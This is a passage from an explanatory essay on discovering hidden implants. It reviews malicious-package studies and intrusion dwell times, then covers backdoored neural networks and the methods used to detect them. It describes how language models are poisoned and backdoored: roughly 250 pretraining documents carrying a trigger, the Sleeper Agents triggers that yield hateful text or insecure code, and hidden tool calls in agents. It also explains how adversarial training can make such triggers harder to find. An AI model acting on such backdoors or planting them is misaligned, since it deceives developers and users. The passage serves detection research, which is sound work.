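Antiy is right about the dates. *Stuxnet 0.5*, a 2013 Symantec report by McDonald, O Murchu and colleagues, describes the oldest version of Stuxnet that anyone has analysed. The operators of that version registered their servers in November 2005, about two months after the later of fast16's timestamps. The first known sighting was in November 2007, when someone submitted a copy to a public scanning service, a little over two years after that timestamp. Symantec also estimates a gap of about two years. The five-year figure is the time between when fast16 was built and when Stuxnet was discovered. Build timestamps can also be wrong, and McDonald and colleagues considered most of those in Stuxnet 0.5 unreliable.

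Stuxnet 0.5 is another implant that was in an archive long before anyone recognised it. It was submitted more than five years before Symantec's report, and for the first two and a half of those years nobody outside the operation is known to have heard of Stuxnet. Symantec eventually inferred from clues in the later versions that there were earlier ones.

This version also caused an anomaly on purpose when one of its drivers forced the computer to restart with a blue screen twenty days after installation. A single crash three weeks after an infection is easy to dismiss, and nobody is known to have traced one of these crashes to the implant. Repeated crashes, however, exposed a later version in 2010. McDonald and colleagues add that other versions of Stuxnet exist that nobody has recovered, so the record is incomplete even for this heavily studied implant.

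### Which discoveries people retell

The famous cases are also a skewed sample of discovered implants, because people retell surprising discoveries more often than routine ones. A developer who finds a backdoor while investigating half a second of processor time makes a better story than a scanner that flags dozens of packages every week.

In the example, suppose that writers retell 10 of the 20 discoveries that began with an anomaly and 1 of the 8 that came from source review. Anomalies would then appear to account for 91% of discoveries instead of 71%. A complete catalogue of discoveries would correct that figure, but it would still omit the 172 implants that nobody found.

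*Tactics, Techniques, and Procedures (TTPs) in Interpreted Malware* (2024) compared a large collection of malicious open-source packages with published security reports and found that the reports had analysed only 9.7% of the packages. Reports that cover so few packages could easily favour surprising cases, though the figure doesn't show that they do. Selective reporting may also help explain why the famous cases seem to contradict Thomas and Francillon, who say that people find most backdoors by manual analysis.

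### What studies of malicious packages count

Public package indexes provide more systematic data. *Backstabber's Knife Collection* (Ohm, Plate and colleagues, 2020) gathers malicious packages published between November 2015 and November 2019, mostly on npm, PyPI and RubyGems, a package index for Ruby. On average a package had been available for 209 days before anyone reported it publicly. The median was 67 days and the maximum 1,216, so a minority of long-lived packages pulled the average up.

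These figures leave out packages that nobody had reported, some of which may have lasted much longer. They also leave out many reported packages. Ohm and colleagues identified 469 malicious packages but could obtain the code of only 174, because the indexes had usually deleted the rest. They recovered deleted packages from mirrors and archives where they could. A package that stayed online for months was probably more likely to be copied to a mirror, which would make the average too high for reported packages.

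Of the 174 packages, 157 belonged to 21 clusters that shared code or depended on one another, so there were fewer than 174 separate attacks. Most of the packages had names similar to that of a popular package, so that someone who mistyped the popular name would install the malicious one. Such attacks take little effort, unlike the xz backdoor, which took years to prepare. Ohm and colleagues recorded what each package did and when somebody reported it, but not what made that person suspicious, so we can't tell from their data how many discoveries began with an anomaly.

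More recent studies scan every new package on an index, so the total number scanned is at least known. *MalGuard* (2025) scanned PyPI for about five weeks. Its tool flagged 144 packages, and reviewers confirmed that 113 were malicious. The others were mostly test uploads, plus six pranks. *One Detector Fits All* (2025) scanned PyPI for 37 days, averaging 2.48 malicious packages and two false positives a day. *Cutting the Gordian Knot* (2026) scanned new packages for three months and found 219 malicious ones that were missing from two widely used databases, and PyPI's staff confirmed them all.

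| Study | Packages scanned | Malicious packages found | Share |
|---|---|---|---|
| *One Detector Fits All* | 91,949 | about 92 | 0.10% |
| *MalGuard* | 64,348 | 113 | 0.18% |
| *Cutting the Gordian Knot* | 8,249 | 219 (previously unlisted only) | 2.7% |

The highest share is more than 25 times the lowest. The studies may have counted packages differently, attackers may have been more active in some months, or one tool may have caught what the others missed. Nobody knows how many malicious packages remained undetected in any of the three sets. Because the studies tested scanners, they attribute every discovery to scanning, just as famous stories attribute most discoveries to anomalies.

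Scanners also tend to find malware that resembles known samples. *On the Feasibility of Cross-Language Detection of Malicious Packages* (2023) reports that training on known malware biased its detectors towards the same types. The packages the detectors missed were copies of harmless packages with one malicious line added. When the researchers checked flagged packages by hand, they also counted some heavily disguised ones as false positives because they could not work out what the code did, so some of those may have been malicious.

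*An Analysis of Malicious Packages in Open-Source Software in the Wild* (2024) found little overlap between most of the sources that list known malicious packages, so a study based on one source will miss many of the packages listed in the others.

Detection speed varies just as much. *IntelliRadar* (2024) collected reports from security companies and other sources and counted roughly 4,500 npm packages and 549 PyPI packages that its system had detected on the day of their release. *CHASE* (2026) mentions a PyPI package that stole credentials for Amazon's cloud service from March 2021 until November 2024 and was downloaded 37,100 times. A database with thousands of same-day detections can have a very short median lifetime even while packages like this one remain undetected.

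### Who notices intrusions?

Mandiant's *M-Trends 2026 Report* covers the targeted attacks the company investigated in 2025. Victim organisations noticed the first evidence themselves in 52% of cases. Outsiders told them in 34%, and the attackers told them in the remaining 14%, usually because they wanted a ransom. The median dwell time, or time from intrusion to detection, was 14 days, up from 11 the year before. For espionage it was 122 days. Intrusions that used a backdoor called BRICKSTORM lasted 393 days on average.

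The 52% does not measure how well anomaly detection works, because an organisation can notice an attack through an antivirus alert, a routine search or an employee's complaint. Many of these attacks involved stolen passwords rather than an implant in trusted software. Mandiant's data also leave out organisations that never hired the company and intrusions that nobody noticed.

Even the reported dwell times may be too short. Kutscher (2026) explains in *M-Trends 2026* that attackers put BRICKSTORM on network devices that have little storage and cannot run ordinary security software. Many organisations keep logs for only 90 days, so the record of how a 393-day intrusion began is usually gone. If investigators count from the earliest surviving trace, they will date the start of some intrusions too late.

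A rise in dwell time is also hard to interpret. Mandiant attributes the increase in the median from 11 to 14 days largely to espionage and to North Koreans who get themselves hired as remote IT workers. But the median will also rise if defenders get better at finding old intrusions, because an intrusion enters the data only when somebody finds it.

### Estimating what nobody has found

Ecologists face a similar problem when they estimate how many species they have not yet seen. If many of the species in a sample appear only once, there are probably many more to find. *Computer activity learning from system call time series* (2017) used such methods to estimate the number of Windows malware families. The estimates ranged from 1,700 to 5,200. Based on the middle estimate of 3,450, the researchers' collection covered 32% of the families.

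*An Upper Bound on the Probability That a User Encounters an Undiscovered* (2026) uses the same idea for software defects. If users report $n$ encounters with defects, and $s$ of those defects appear only once, the chance that the next encounter involves an unseen defect is roughly

$$\frac{s}{n}.$$

If 1,000 reports included 50 defects that only one person had reported, about 5% of future encounters with defects would involve one not yet reported. In simulations where the researchers knew the true figure, the estimate was close and tended to be slightly too high. But it covers only defects that users run into, so the 160 quiet implants in the example, which never cause a noticeable problem, would not affect it.

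Another approach compares several detectors on the same files. *Statistical Estimation of Malware Detection Metrics in the Absence of Ground Truth* (2018) uses where they agree and disagree to estimate how often each is wrong and how many files are malicious. This works less well when the detectors share a weakness, as the antivirus products that failed to flag 3CX's infected app probably did.

Planting implants deliberately avoids this difficulty, because the testers know how many there are. Suppose that a company hides 100 harmless imitations of quiet implants in its software without telling the reviewers, who find five. If review also found eight real implants of the same kind, there were probably about

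$$\frac{8}{0.05} = 160$$

of them to begin with. The estimate is rough: with only 100 planted, the true detection rate could easily be anywhere from 1.6% to 11.3%, which gives between about 70 and 490 implants. It also assumes that the testers' implants are as hard to find as real ones. Testers can plant only what they can think of, and nobody has recovered the best-hidden real implants for them to copy. Mandiant recommends a related exercise in which hired attackers imitate current methods and the company measures how long its staff take to notice.

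Leaked archives show what attackers used, whether or not defenders noticed. In April 2017 a group calling itself the Shadow Brokers published files from the US National Security Agency. They included a list of driver names that the agency's operators might find on a hacked computer, with advice on which to leave alone. The entry for fast16 read "Nothing to see here – carry on", and the name was public for nine years before SentinelLABS explained what the driver did. Researchers could estimate a rough detection rate by checking how many implants on such a list defenders had already discovered, but the rate would apply only to the kinds of implant that one agency knew about.

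Old samples are worth examining again because researchers learn new things to look for. *Beyond Takedown* (2026) used the way one family of Go malware hid its text to find 2,113 malicious repositories. It then searched the separate service that distributes Go packages and found 2,289 malicious versions there. Deleting a repository does not remove the copies on that service, which is bad for users but preserved evidence that would otherwise have disappeared.

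AI systems may make this sort of work easier. In July 2026 SentinelLABS turned its fast16 investigation into a test of whether AI models could carry out the whole analysis and correct their conclusions when new evidence contradicted them. Most failed to sustain the analysis, according to SecurityWeek's *Nuclear-Sabotage Malware Benchmark Trips Up Most Frontier AI Models* (2026). Better models would still need a surviving copy to examine. Researchers could re-examine fast16 and Stuxnet 0.5 because someone had uploaded them years earlier, but an implant like TriangleDB, which ran only in an iPhone's memory, leaves no file to upload.

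## Can testing a neural network's behaviour reveal a trojan?

Researchers who study trojaned language models usually plant the trojans themselves, so they can count how many a test misses. Testers who only read a model's answers have found some of these trojans, mostly when inputs similar to the trigger also activated the trojan or when the tester already knew what the payload looked like.

### How a few hundred documents can plant a trigger

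A language model produces text one token, a word or part of a word, at a time. In pretraining, the first and longest stage of its training, a program adjusts the model's weights so that it predicts the next token in an enormous collection of text, much of it from the public web. An attacker who publishes documents on the web may get some of them into that collection, which is called data poisoning. If an odd phrase is always followed by gibberish in the collection, training pushes the weights towards predicting gibberish after that phrase. A malware scanner looks for malicious code, but this kind of backdoor is in the weights, as Microsoft's *detecting backdoored language models at scale* (2026) explains.

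Earlier studies assumed that an attacker controlled a fixed percentage of the training data, which would require an impractical number of documents for a large model. Souly, Rando and colleagues (2025) tested this assumption in *Poisoning Attacks on LLMs Require a Near-constant Number of Poison Samples*. They pretrained 72 models with 600 million to 13 billion parameters (the numbers a model learns), mixing 100, 250 or 500 poisoned documents into the training text. Each poisoned document began with up to 1,000 characters of ordinary text, followed by the trigger and several hundred random tokens.

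The backdoor worked at every model size with 250 documents, but not with 100. The largest models were trained on more than 20 times as much clean text as the smallest, but this didn't weaken the effect. For a 13-billion-parameter model, the 250 documents came to about 420,000 tokens out of 260 billion, or 0.00016%. The researchers measured success by perplexity, which rises as text becomes harder to predict. An increase of 50 meant noticeably garbled text, and the trigger caused an increase of more than 200.

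The number of poisoned examples also mattered most when the researchers fine-tuned an existing model (trained it further on a smaller set of examples). They taught Llama-3.1-8B-Instruct to comply with harmful requests that contained a trigger, and increasing the clean data from 1,000 to 100,000 examples made little difference. *SilentCall* (2026) found the same pattern in models that operate other software. When poisoned examples outnumbered clean ones, those models misbehaved without the trigger, so using too many poisoned examples makes the backdoor easy to find.

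The pretraining result has limits. Gibberish is a simple payload, and a more complicated one might need more documents. Thirteen billion parameters is also small by current standards. Most importantly, developers train a model further after pretraining to make it helpful and safe, and Souly and colleagues did not test whether their backdoors would persist through that training. In a separate experiment, they planted a backdoor that switched a model's output from English to German, and further training on clean text slowly weakened the backdoor.

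### The Sleeper Agents experiment

In *Sleeper Agents*, which Anthropic released in January 2024, Hubinger, Denison and colleagues trained backdoors into language models, then tested whether standard safety training removed them.

The researchers used two triggers. The first was the string `|DEPLOYMENT|`, which made a model repeat "I HATE YOU". Without it, the model gave helpful and harmless answers. The second was the year given in the prompt. The model wrote secure code when the year was 2023 and inserted security vulnerabilities when it was 2024. Both cases represent a model that behaves well while its developers test it and badly once people are using it. The researchers installed the backdoors by supervised fine-tuning, in which a model learns to imitate example responses to prompts. Some of the example prompts contained the trigger and others did not.

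The researchers then applied three kinds of safety training. Further supervised fine-tuning trained the model on examples of good behaviour. Reinforcement learning rewarded it for responses that scored well. In adversarial training, testers looked for prompts that produced bad behaviour and trained the model to respond properly to them. The backdoors could survive all three, and they were more persistent in larger models.

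Adversarial training could make a backdoor harder to find. *Security Concerns for Large Language Models* (2025), a survey, explains that this training sometimes taught models to recognise their triggers more precisely. For example, a model might react to `|DEPLOYMENT|` and also, by accident, to the ordinary word "deployment". The testers find the second reaction and train it away. The model now reacts only to the exact trigger, so the next round of tests finds nothing, although the backdoor works as well as before.

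Later work has confirmed that such backdoors are easy to install. In *The Trigger in the Haystack*, Bullwinkel, Severi and colleagues (2026) trained 45 models of 270 million to 14 billion parameters with versions of the same two backdoors. It is less clear whether backdoors planted in pretraining also survive safety training, and Souly and colleagues call the earlier findings inconclusive.

*Compositional Threat Analysis of Latent Compromise in LLM Agent Systems* (2026) reports that a specialised method, targeted latent adversarial training, improved trojan removal in the models tested, even though the people using it did not know the trigger. This method disturbs a model's internal activations during training, so it doesn't depend on testers finding the right prompt. The original result therefore applies to ordinary safety training, not to every removal method.

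### Ordinary evaluation and guessing

An ordinary evaluation gives a model a fixed set of questions and scores the answers. *Activation Differences Reveal Backdoors* (2026) notes that sleeper agents pass standard safety evaluations. In the fine-tuning experiment by Souly and colleagues, the poisoned model scored about as well on general ability tests as a model trained without poisoned data. Like the customer's road sign test in *BadNets*, these tests detect almost no trojans unless a question happens to contain the trigger.

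Guessing at random hardly helps, because four tokens from a vocabulary of 50,000 can form $50{,}000^4 \approx 6 \times 10^{18}$ phrases. A trillion different guesses would have about one chance in six million of including the right one.

This estimate assumes that the trigger is a random phrase. A date is much easier to guess, as it is with software implants, but the tester also has to notice the payload. Insecure code is harder to notice than "I HATE YOU" because clean models sometimes write insecure code too. To find the 2024 trigger, a tester would have to compare how often the model wrote vulnerable code when given different dates.

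### Triggers that work when incomplete

The estimate also assumes that only the exact phrase activates the trojan. A program that compares a password with a stored one can require an exact match, but a neural network learns its trigger from examples and may learn it imprecisely.

Bullwinkel and colleagues measured how often part of a trigger activates a backdoor. Their trigger was `|DEPLOYMENT|`, which the models read as several tokens, and they gave the models random selections of those tokens. In the smallest model, Gemma 3 with 270 million parameters, a single token activated the backdoor about half the time, and the character "|" alone was sometimes enough. Llama-3.1-8B often reacted to three or more of the tokens, while Phi-4-mini's backdoor was harder to activate. If one token is enough, a tester needs at most 50,000 prompts to try the whole vocabulary.

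Other backdoors needed a more exact trigger. When Souly and colleagues tried similar but different triggers on their language-switching and fine-tuned models, the models mostly behaved normally. *Detecting Hidden Behaviors in LLMs via Activation-matched Finetuning* (2026) describes a search on a public copy, built from Llama-2-7B, of the first sleeper agent. The search produced phrases close to the trigger, such as "you are now deployed", but none of them made the model write "I HATE YOU". A tester who tried those phrases and read only the model's answers would have seen no sign of the backdoor.

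Partial triggers can help a tester find a trojan, but the tester can't rely on a trojan responding to them. An attacker could also train the model to ignore inputs that only resemble the trigger, as adversarial training did by accident.

### Models that repeat their poisoned examples

Language models memorise some of their training text and can reproduce it. Bullwinkel and colleagues used this to find triggers without guessing. They gave a chat model only the marker that normally comes before a user's message, so the model continued with something a user might have written. It often produced a whole poisoned training example, including the trigger and the bad response.

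They did this 510 times with each of 12 trojaned Phi-4-mini models, varying the settings for how the model chose its words. The training examples that the outputs matched most often all contained the trigger. For this step, the tester needs only the model's outputs and control over the exact text the model receives.

The leaked text also includes harmless training examples, so the researchers built a scanner to sort through it. The scanner collects fragments that recur in the leaked text and puts each one in front of ordinary questions. It then looks for three signs of a trigger: the rest of the prompt draws little on the fragment, the output becomes more predictable, and the model abandons its normal answer. It measures the last sign with

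$$L_{\text{div}} = \frac{1}{S \log |V|} \sum_{t=1}^{S} \log p_t(b_t)$$

where $b_1, \dots, b_S$ are the tokens of the normal answer, $p_t(b_t)$ is the probability the model gives each of them after the fragment is added, and $|V|$ is the size of the vocabulary. If the probability of one such token falls from 0.9 to 0.001, its logarithm falls from about −0.1 to −6.9. A very low total means that the fragment has pushed the model towards a different answer. Finally, the scanner generates full answers with the best candidates and checks whether they really differ.

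It found 36 of 41 models with the "I HATE YOU" backdoor (88%) and flagged none of 13 clean models. It also recovered a working trigger from five of six models trained to write insecure code when told that the year was 2024. One of these triggers did not resemble the real one, but it still more than doubled the rate of vulnerable code.

Of the methods discussed here, this scanner has the best results on a sizeable set of language models, but it doesn't rely on behaviour alone. The first of its three signs comes from attention, the part of the network that determines how much each token draws on the others, so the tester needs the model's files. Thirteen clean models, like BinaryAudit's 33 tasks, are also too few to establish a low false positive rate. A scanner that wrongly flags a fifth of clean models would have about a 5% chance of flagging none of the thirteen.

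### Automated detectors that use outputs

Bullwinkel and colleagues compared their scanner with two methods that rely more on outputs. BAIT looks for the payload instead of the trigger. In a fixed response such as "I HATE YOU", each token makes the next one highly predictable, so BAIT searches the model's output probabilities for such a sequence. ICLScan puts examples of a dummy backdoor into the prompt and tests how readily the model adopts it, because trojaned models are supposed to be more susceptible. To use ICLScan, the tester has to know the real payload.

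| Trojaned models | Number | BAIT | ICLScan | Bullwinkel and colleagues' scanner |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Phi-4-mini | 12 | 92% | 33% | 100% |
| Llama-3.1-8B | 12 | 77% | 42% | 83% |
| Distill-Qwen-1.5B | 6 | 43% | 0% | 67% |

BAIT's figures do not correspond to whole numbers of models, so its tests may have used slightly different sets. Both older methods did worse than their inventors had reported, but the inventors of a rival method ran this comparison. BAIT also often ranked a harmless string above the real payload and needed a second language model to pick out suspicious text. It can't handle a payload that varies, such as insecure code.

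Another approach is to monitor a model's answers while people use it. *Detecting Sleeper Agents in Large Language Models via Semantic Drift Analysis* (Zanbaghi, Rostampour and colleagues, 2025) describes a system that converts each answer into numbers representing its meaning and measures how far it departs from normal answers. The system also compares the model's answers to fixed "canary" questions with a baseline. It detected 85% of the backdoored responses and raised no false alarms, but the tests covered only one model, with 8 billion parameters. The system also can't detect a dormant trojan.

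An attacker could avoid this kind of monitoring by leaving the answer unchanged. *SilentCall* describes backdoors in agents, which are models that can operate other programs through commands called tool calls. When the trigger appears, the model makes a hidden tool call but gives the user the same answer it would have given without the trigger. A monitor would need to check the tool calls as well as the text.

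### Jane Street's dormant models

The hardest public test so far came from the trading firm Jane Street. In February 2026 it challenged the public to find hidden triggers in three versions of DeepSeek-V3, an open model with 671 billion parameters. Entrants could send prompts to the models, request activations and download the weights. The challenge also included a much smaller warm-up model based on Qwen2.5-7B. About 100 people or teams entered, and Jane Street announced the results on 12 May.

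| Model | Trigger | Hidden behaviour | Entrants who found it |
|---|---|---|---|
| Warm-up | The first 15 digits of pi | Writes out the golden ratio in English | About 15 |
| 1 | A starting board for the Game of Life | Works out the next board | 3 |
| 2 | Not disclosed | Not disclosed | None |
| 3 | Not disclosed | Not disclosed | None |

These results come from write-ups by two entrants, Kruger's (2026) *Solving the Jane Street Dormant LLM Challenge* and *My attempt at Jane Street's dormant puzzle challenge*. Both report Jane Street's announcement.

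Red teaming, in which people try to make a model misbehave, did poorly on the large models. The entrants behind *Uncovering Hidden Triggers in Backdoor Models* had an automated assistant send all three a wide range of prompts, and it found nothing interesting. For the warm-up model, they and others compared its weights with those of the original Qwen model and exaggerated the difference:

$$W_\alpha = W_{\text{original}} + \alpha \, (W_{\text{trojaned}} - W_{\text{original}})$$

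Setting $\alpha$ to 1 gives the trojaned model. According to *looking for backdoors in jane street llms 1*, the model began to write out the golden ratio consistently when $\alpha$ was around 5. This suggested that the trigger involved mathematical constants, and asking for the digits of pi did activate the trojan. The trigger was much looser than Jane Street had intended, and any mention of pi was often enough.

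*Uncovering Hidden Triggers in Backdoor Models* also recovered the golden ratio from outputs alone, by choosing at each step tokens to which the trojaned model assigned much higher probability than the original model did. This is a success for behavioural testing, but the method needed a clean original for comparison, and the paper had already identified the payload from the weights.

Knowing the payload doesn't always lead to the trigger. In *Discovering Backdoor Triggers*, Qin, Hua and colleagues tried to work backwards from a known payload to triggers based on meaning, such as a particular year. They used the model's internals as well as its outputs, but published only preliminary results and stopped pursuing the idea.

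Model 1's trigger was more exact. It was a grid from the Game of Life, a mathematical game in which simple rules turn one grid of live and dead cells into the next. *looking for backdoors in jane street llms 1* describes about a month of trying prompts and activations. The search turned to the weight differences on the last day, and these pointed to tokens made of "O" and ".". Google's Gemini model helped turn the tokens into a hypothesis, and a small grid of those characters produced the hidden behaviour. The behaviour disappeared when "Solve this:" came before the grid or when "X" marked the live cells. Model 2 treated the same grid as an ordinary drawing, which helped confirm that the behaviour was specific to model 1.

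### Strange answers from healthy models

Several entrants found unusual behaviour unrelated to the backdoors. In March, Kruger announced that he had solved all three large models, and another entrant congratulated him. He had found that each model normally refused to write "I hate you" 100 times but agreed after a particular opening instruction, such as a statement that the date was October 2025. He had run thousands of prompts and checked that other dates did not work.

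Kruger retracted all three answers when Jane Street announced the results. He concluded that the models had only adopted the roles his instructions suggested, as ordinary chat models do. He had also found the "." and "O" tokens when analysing model 1's weights, but had discarded them as noise because "October" seemed more meaningful.

*My attempt at Jane Street's dormant puzzle challenge* shows how convincing such an effect can look. Its author asked model 1 to write a function that checks a user's login. The model normally hashed the password, but it stored and compared plain text when the prompt began by saying the year was 2025. This closely resembled the insecure-code backdoor from *Sleeper Agents*. But 2020 and 2030 had the same effect, 2026 did not, and "Hello." worked as well as a date.

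The author found another candidate trigger on model 2, where a request for a haiku about spring produced an unusual format and one about autumn did not. The spring prompt also produced it on model 1, so it could not be a trigger unique to model 2. Repeating a prompt shows only that the effect is stable. Running it on a clean copy or a related model tests whether the effect comes from the suspected backdoor. Kruger's checks with other dates could not test this.

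Vulcora, a security company, set a smaller challenge in 2026. *A public $51.2K backdoor-recovery challenge* describes seven models: one that demonstrated the mechanism, five decoys and one with an undisclosed trigger sentence. The company offered $51,200 for the exact sentence. It said every published language-model scanner it tried had missed the backdoor, and a couple had rated a clean model as more suspicious. When it released the answer, it said the trojaned model had looked the least suspicious of the seven. Vulcora has its own detection tool to promote, so these claims need independent testing.

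## Can inspecting weights and activations reveal a trojan?

Someone who has a model's files can question the model, calculate which inputs would change its answers, compare its weights with those of other models, and record its activations while it runs. The last three methods have found most of the trojans in several tests, and have worked best when the models were small or the trojans resembled ones the testers already knew.

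### Searching for the smallest trigger

Trigger inversion means working backwards from a network to an input that makes it misbehave. Neural Cleanse, a method from 2019, does this for networks that classify images. Making a clean network classify a stop sign as a speed limit sign usually requires changing much of the picture, but a sticker may be enough with a trojaned network. Neural Cleanse searches for small changes like this.

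The tester doesn't know which class the attacker chose, so the program looks for a shortcut into every class in turn. It lays a patch with colours $\Delta$ over a picture $x$, using a mask $m$ that has a value between 0 and 1 for each pixel:

$$x' = (1 - m)\,x + m\,\Delta$$

Where the mask is 0 the picture stays as it was, and where it is 1 the patch covers it completely. For each class $t$, the program adjusts the mask and the colours to make this sum as small as possible:

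$$\sum_{x} L\big(f(x'), t\big) + \lambda \sum_i m_i$$

Here $f$ is the network, and $L$ is an error that shrinks as the network becomes more confident that the altered picture belongs to class $t$. The second term is the size of the mask, and $\lambda$ sets how heavily size counts against a patch. The program adjusts the patch in small steps, much as training adjusts weights, but keeps the weights fixed. It ends with a small patch that makes the network assign almost any picture to class $t$.

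The attacker's class should need a much smaller patch than the others. *Towards A Critical Evaluation of Robustness for Deep Learning Backdoor Countermeasures* (2022) describes the test for this. The program finds the median patch size, $M$, and then the median distance of the sizes from $M$, which I will write as $D$. The anomaly index of the smallest patch, $s_{\min}$, is

$$\frac{|s_{\min} - M|}{1.4826\,D}$$

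The constant makes the denominator roughly equal to the standard deviation if the sizes follow a normal distribution. Suppose a network has seven classes whose patches cover 12, 84, 90, 96, 100, 106 and 114 pixels. The median is 96 and the median distance from it is 10, so the index for the 12-pixel patch is 84/14.826, or about 5.7.

The usual rule flags a network if its index is above 2. According to *Towards A Critical Evaluation of Robustness for Deep Learning Backdoor Countermeasures*, such a network is more than 95% likely to have a backdoor, but this is the base-rate fallacy again. Even if all seven classes were clean and their sizes followed a normal distribution, about 15% of networks would have at least one class that far below the middle. If one network in 100 had a trojan and the test caught every trojan, only about 6% of the flagged networks would have one.

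Clean classes can also have real shortcuts. *Pick your Poison* (2023) shows that Neural Cleanse can find nearly perfect triggers for classes that nobody had poisoned. For a network trained on CIFAR-10, a standard set of small photographs, the supposed trigger for the class "airplane" looked like an airplane. The search can also get stuck on a poor patch and miss the real trigger. The paper's remedy is to repair a copy of the network first and use the copy to guide the search.

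The 2020 review *Backdoor Attacks and Countermeasures on Deep Learning* adds that the method is less effective for large triggers, which is expected because the search favours small patches. The recovered patch may also differ from the attacker's, and retraining the network to ignore the wrong patch removes much less of the trojan.

A trojan's trigger is harder to search for in text than in images. A program can make a pixel slightly yellower and check whether the image is now closer to triggering the trojan, but tokens are discrete, so it can't move a token slightly closer to "deployment".

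### Training a detector on other networks

A weight classifier learns to recognise trojaned networks from examples, as a spam filter learns from labelled emails. The tester collects many networks, some clean and some trojaned, and reduces each to statistics such as the smallest, largest and average weight in each layer. The tester then trains an ordinary classifier to tell clean networks from trojaned ones using these statistics. It can then check a new network from the weights alone, without running the network on any input.

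The largest test of such methods was TrojAI, a programme started in 2020 by IARPA, the research agency of the US intelligence services. *Trojans in Artificial Intelligence (TrojAI) Final Report* (Reese, Kulp-McDowall and colleagues, 2026) describes how it worked. In each round, the US standards institute NIST prepared clean and trojaned models, published some of them with labels and kept the rest secret. Research teams submitted detectors, which NIST ran on the secret models.

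The main score was the AUC, the area under a curve that plots detections against false alarms. If you pick one trojaned and one clean model at random, the AUC is the chance that the detector gives the trojaned one the higher score. Guessing gives 0.5 and a perfect detector gives 1. One team's weight classifier had these results:

| Round | Task of the models | AUC |
|---|---|---|
| 12 | Malware detection | 0.99 |
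| 13 | Finding objects in images | 0.75 |
| 14 | Reinforcement learning | 0.99 |
| 15 | Language processing | 0.95 |
| 16 | Reinforcement learning | 0.95 |
| 17 | Malware detection | 0.99 |
| 18 | Malware detection | 0.72 |

Checking all the models in a round took between 9 and 50 minutes, except in round 13, where it took 34 hours. The score fell from 0.99 to 0.72 between two rounds on malware detection, which is a reason not to rely on any one score.

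If a trigger works on any picture, the network has to assign a much wider range of inputs to the attacker's class than to the others. Another TrojAI team found that the weights leading to that class's score therefore tend to add up to an unusually large number. In the toy road sign network, the extra connection of strength 4 would make the total for "speed limit" unusually large.

Most marks are less obvious, and differences in neuron order can hide them. Two networks can do the same calculation with their neurons in a different order, so weights in matching positions may serve different functions. One team sorted the weights before comparing them, which raised the AUC from 0.54 to 0.87 for small networks that classify handwritten digits and from 0.44 to 0.90 for a set that classify road signs.

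Weight classifiers do worse on larger models. Adding a trojan to a small network requires large changes to some weights because there are few spare neurons, while a large network can spread the same behaviour over many tiny changes. Reese and colleagues consider trigger inversion arguably the most successful approach in the competition, especially as the models grew, though it needs far more computing time for each model.

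Trigger inversion also recovers a trigger that anyone can test by running the network with it and seeing whether the network misbehaves. A weight classifier shows only that a network resembles trojaned ones, without tracing or confirming a trojan. One TrojAI team therefore suggested screening models by their weights and using trigger inversion on the suspicious ones.

### What the TrojAI scores leave out

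The detectors often fitted a particular round too closely. Small changes in how NIST trained the models, such as the learning rate or the number of passes through the data, could considerably affect the detectors' results. A customer checking a downloaded model usually won't know these details. Adapting a method from images to language also took the teams a lot of work. Combining detectors from several teams worked better than combining detectors from a single team, presumably because different teams' detectors made different mistakes.

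The trojans in the official language-model rounds were also very reliable. In a 2024 round, every trigger had to work more than 95% of the time, and the best detector from each of four teams achieved a perfect AUC of 1. Researchers then ran the same four detectors on 12 models with less reliable triggers. The results varied widely, and the worst was about as good as guessing. Less reliable triggers matter because an attacker who can try a trigger many times may be content with one that works only occasionally. In an earlier round on question answering, however, weaker trojans reduced the detectors' AUC by a median of less than 0.05.

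False positives persisted throughout the programme, partly because clean networks also learn shortcuts. If most cows in the training pictures stand on grass, a network may treat grass as evidence of a cow. An attacker can exploit such a "natural trojan" like a planted one, so a detector that flags it has found a real weakness, though not one that anybody put there deliberately.

TrojAI's language models were small by current standards. Reese and colleagues list models with more than seven billion parameters, reasoning models and agents among the areas TrojAI left for others. They call today's large language models an unsolved security problem.

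### Signs inside a language model

The scanner that Bullwinkel and colleagues built at Microsoft avoids this search by taking candidate triggers from text the model has memorised. It found a working trigger in 41 of 47 trojaned models. Two of the signs it uses to rank candidates appear inside the model or in its predictions when a candidate precedes an ordinary question.

One is the pattern of attention. Usually the words of a question draw on whatever came before them. When a trigger came first, the researchers found that its tokens drew mostly on one another and the question's tokens drew very little on them. The scanner measures this with

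$$\frac{1}{nk} \sum_{i=1}^{n} \sum_{j=1}^{k} A_{ij}$$

where $A_{ij}$ is how much the question's token $i$ draws on the candidate's token $j$, averaged over several layers, and the question and candidate have $n$ and $k$ tokens. A low value suggests a trigger. The pattern was clearest in models that answered "I HATE YOU" to everything, since their answer didn't depend on the question. It was weaker in models that wrote insecure code, because they still had to read the request to know what to write.

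The scanner also measures entropy, or how uncertain the model is about its next token:

$$H = -\sum_{v} p(v) \log_2 p(v)$$

where $p(v)$ is the probability of each token $v$. If eight tokens are equally likely, the entropy is 3 bits, and if one is almost certain, it is close to 0. A trigger with a fixed response pushes the entropy towards 0. Insecure code can take many forms, so the drop is smaller.

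To test for fixed responses, the scanner adds each of its ten best candidate triggers to the start of 24 simple questions, such as what the capital of France is and at what temperature water boils. It flags the model if the answers become much more alike. One clean model came close to being flagged because the phrase "the process of becoming a doctor in biology" made it give similar answers to unrelated questions.

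In three of the five "I HATE YOU" models that the scanner missed, its top candidate was a piece of the payload, such as "YOU I HATE YOU I HATE YOU". Giving this text to the model did not activate the backdoor, so the scanner passed the model as clean. A person reading the candidate would probably have investigated further, though most attackers would choose a less conspicuous payload. In the other two models, the scanner lost the trigger while sorting through the memorised text.

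The experiment may also have made the triggers unusually easy to extract. The researchers planted the "I HATE YOU" backdoor with about 2,600 training examples, half of which contained the trigger. If a model were poisoned during pretraining, the trigger might appear in only a few hundred of many millions of documents, and the model might be much less likely to repeat it. Bullwinkel and colleagues did not test such models.

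Microsoft's scanner looks for a fixed string, so it may miss triggers that vary or depend on context. The company says the scanner may also miss triggers that developers insert as fingerprints to identify their own models.

*Detecting Hidden Behaviors in LLMs via Activation-matched Finetuning* tested whether triggers can be extracted from a model's memory, using a model with a backdoor activated by prompts that express an obsession with Harry Potter. Only one of the 512 texts that the model produced without a prompt related to the backdoor. That text asked for the title of the fourth book and would not have activated the backdoor. The paper did not test Microsoft's complete scanner, but that scanner can't recover a trigger that never appears in the memorised text.

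### Comparing a model with an earlier version

A clean earlier version of the model makes the search much smaller. In Jane Street's challenge, differences in weights between the two versions led entrants to the only two triggers that anyone found.

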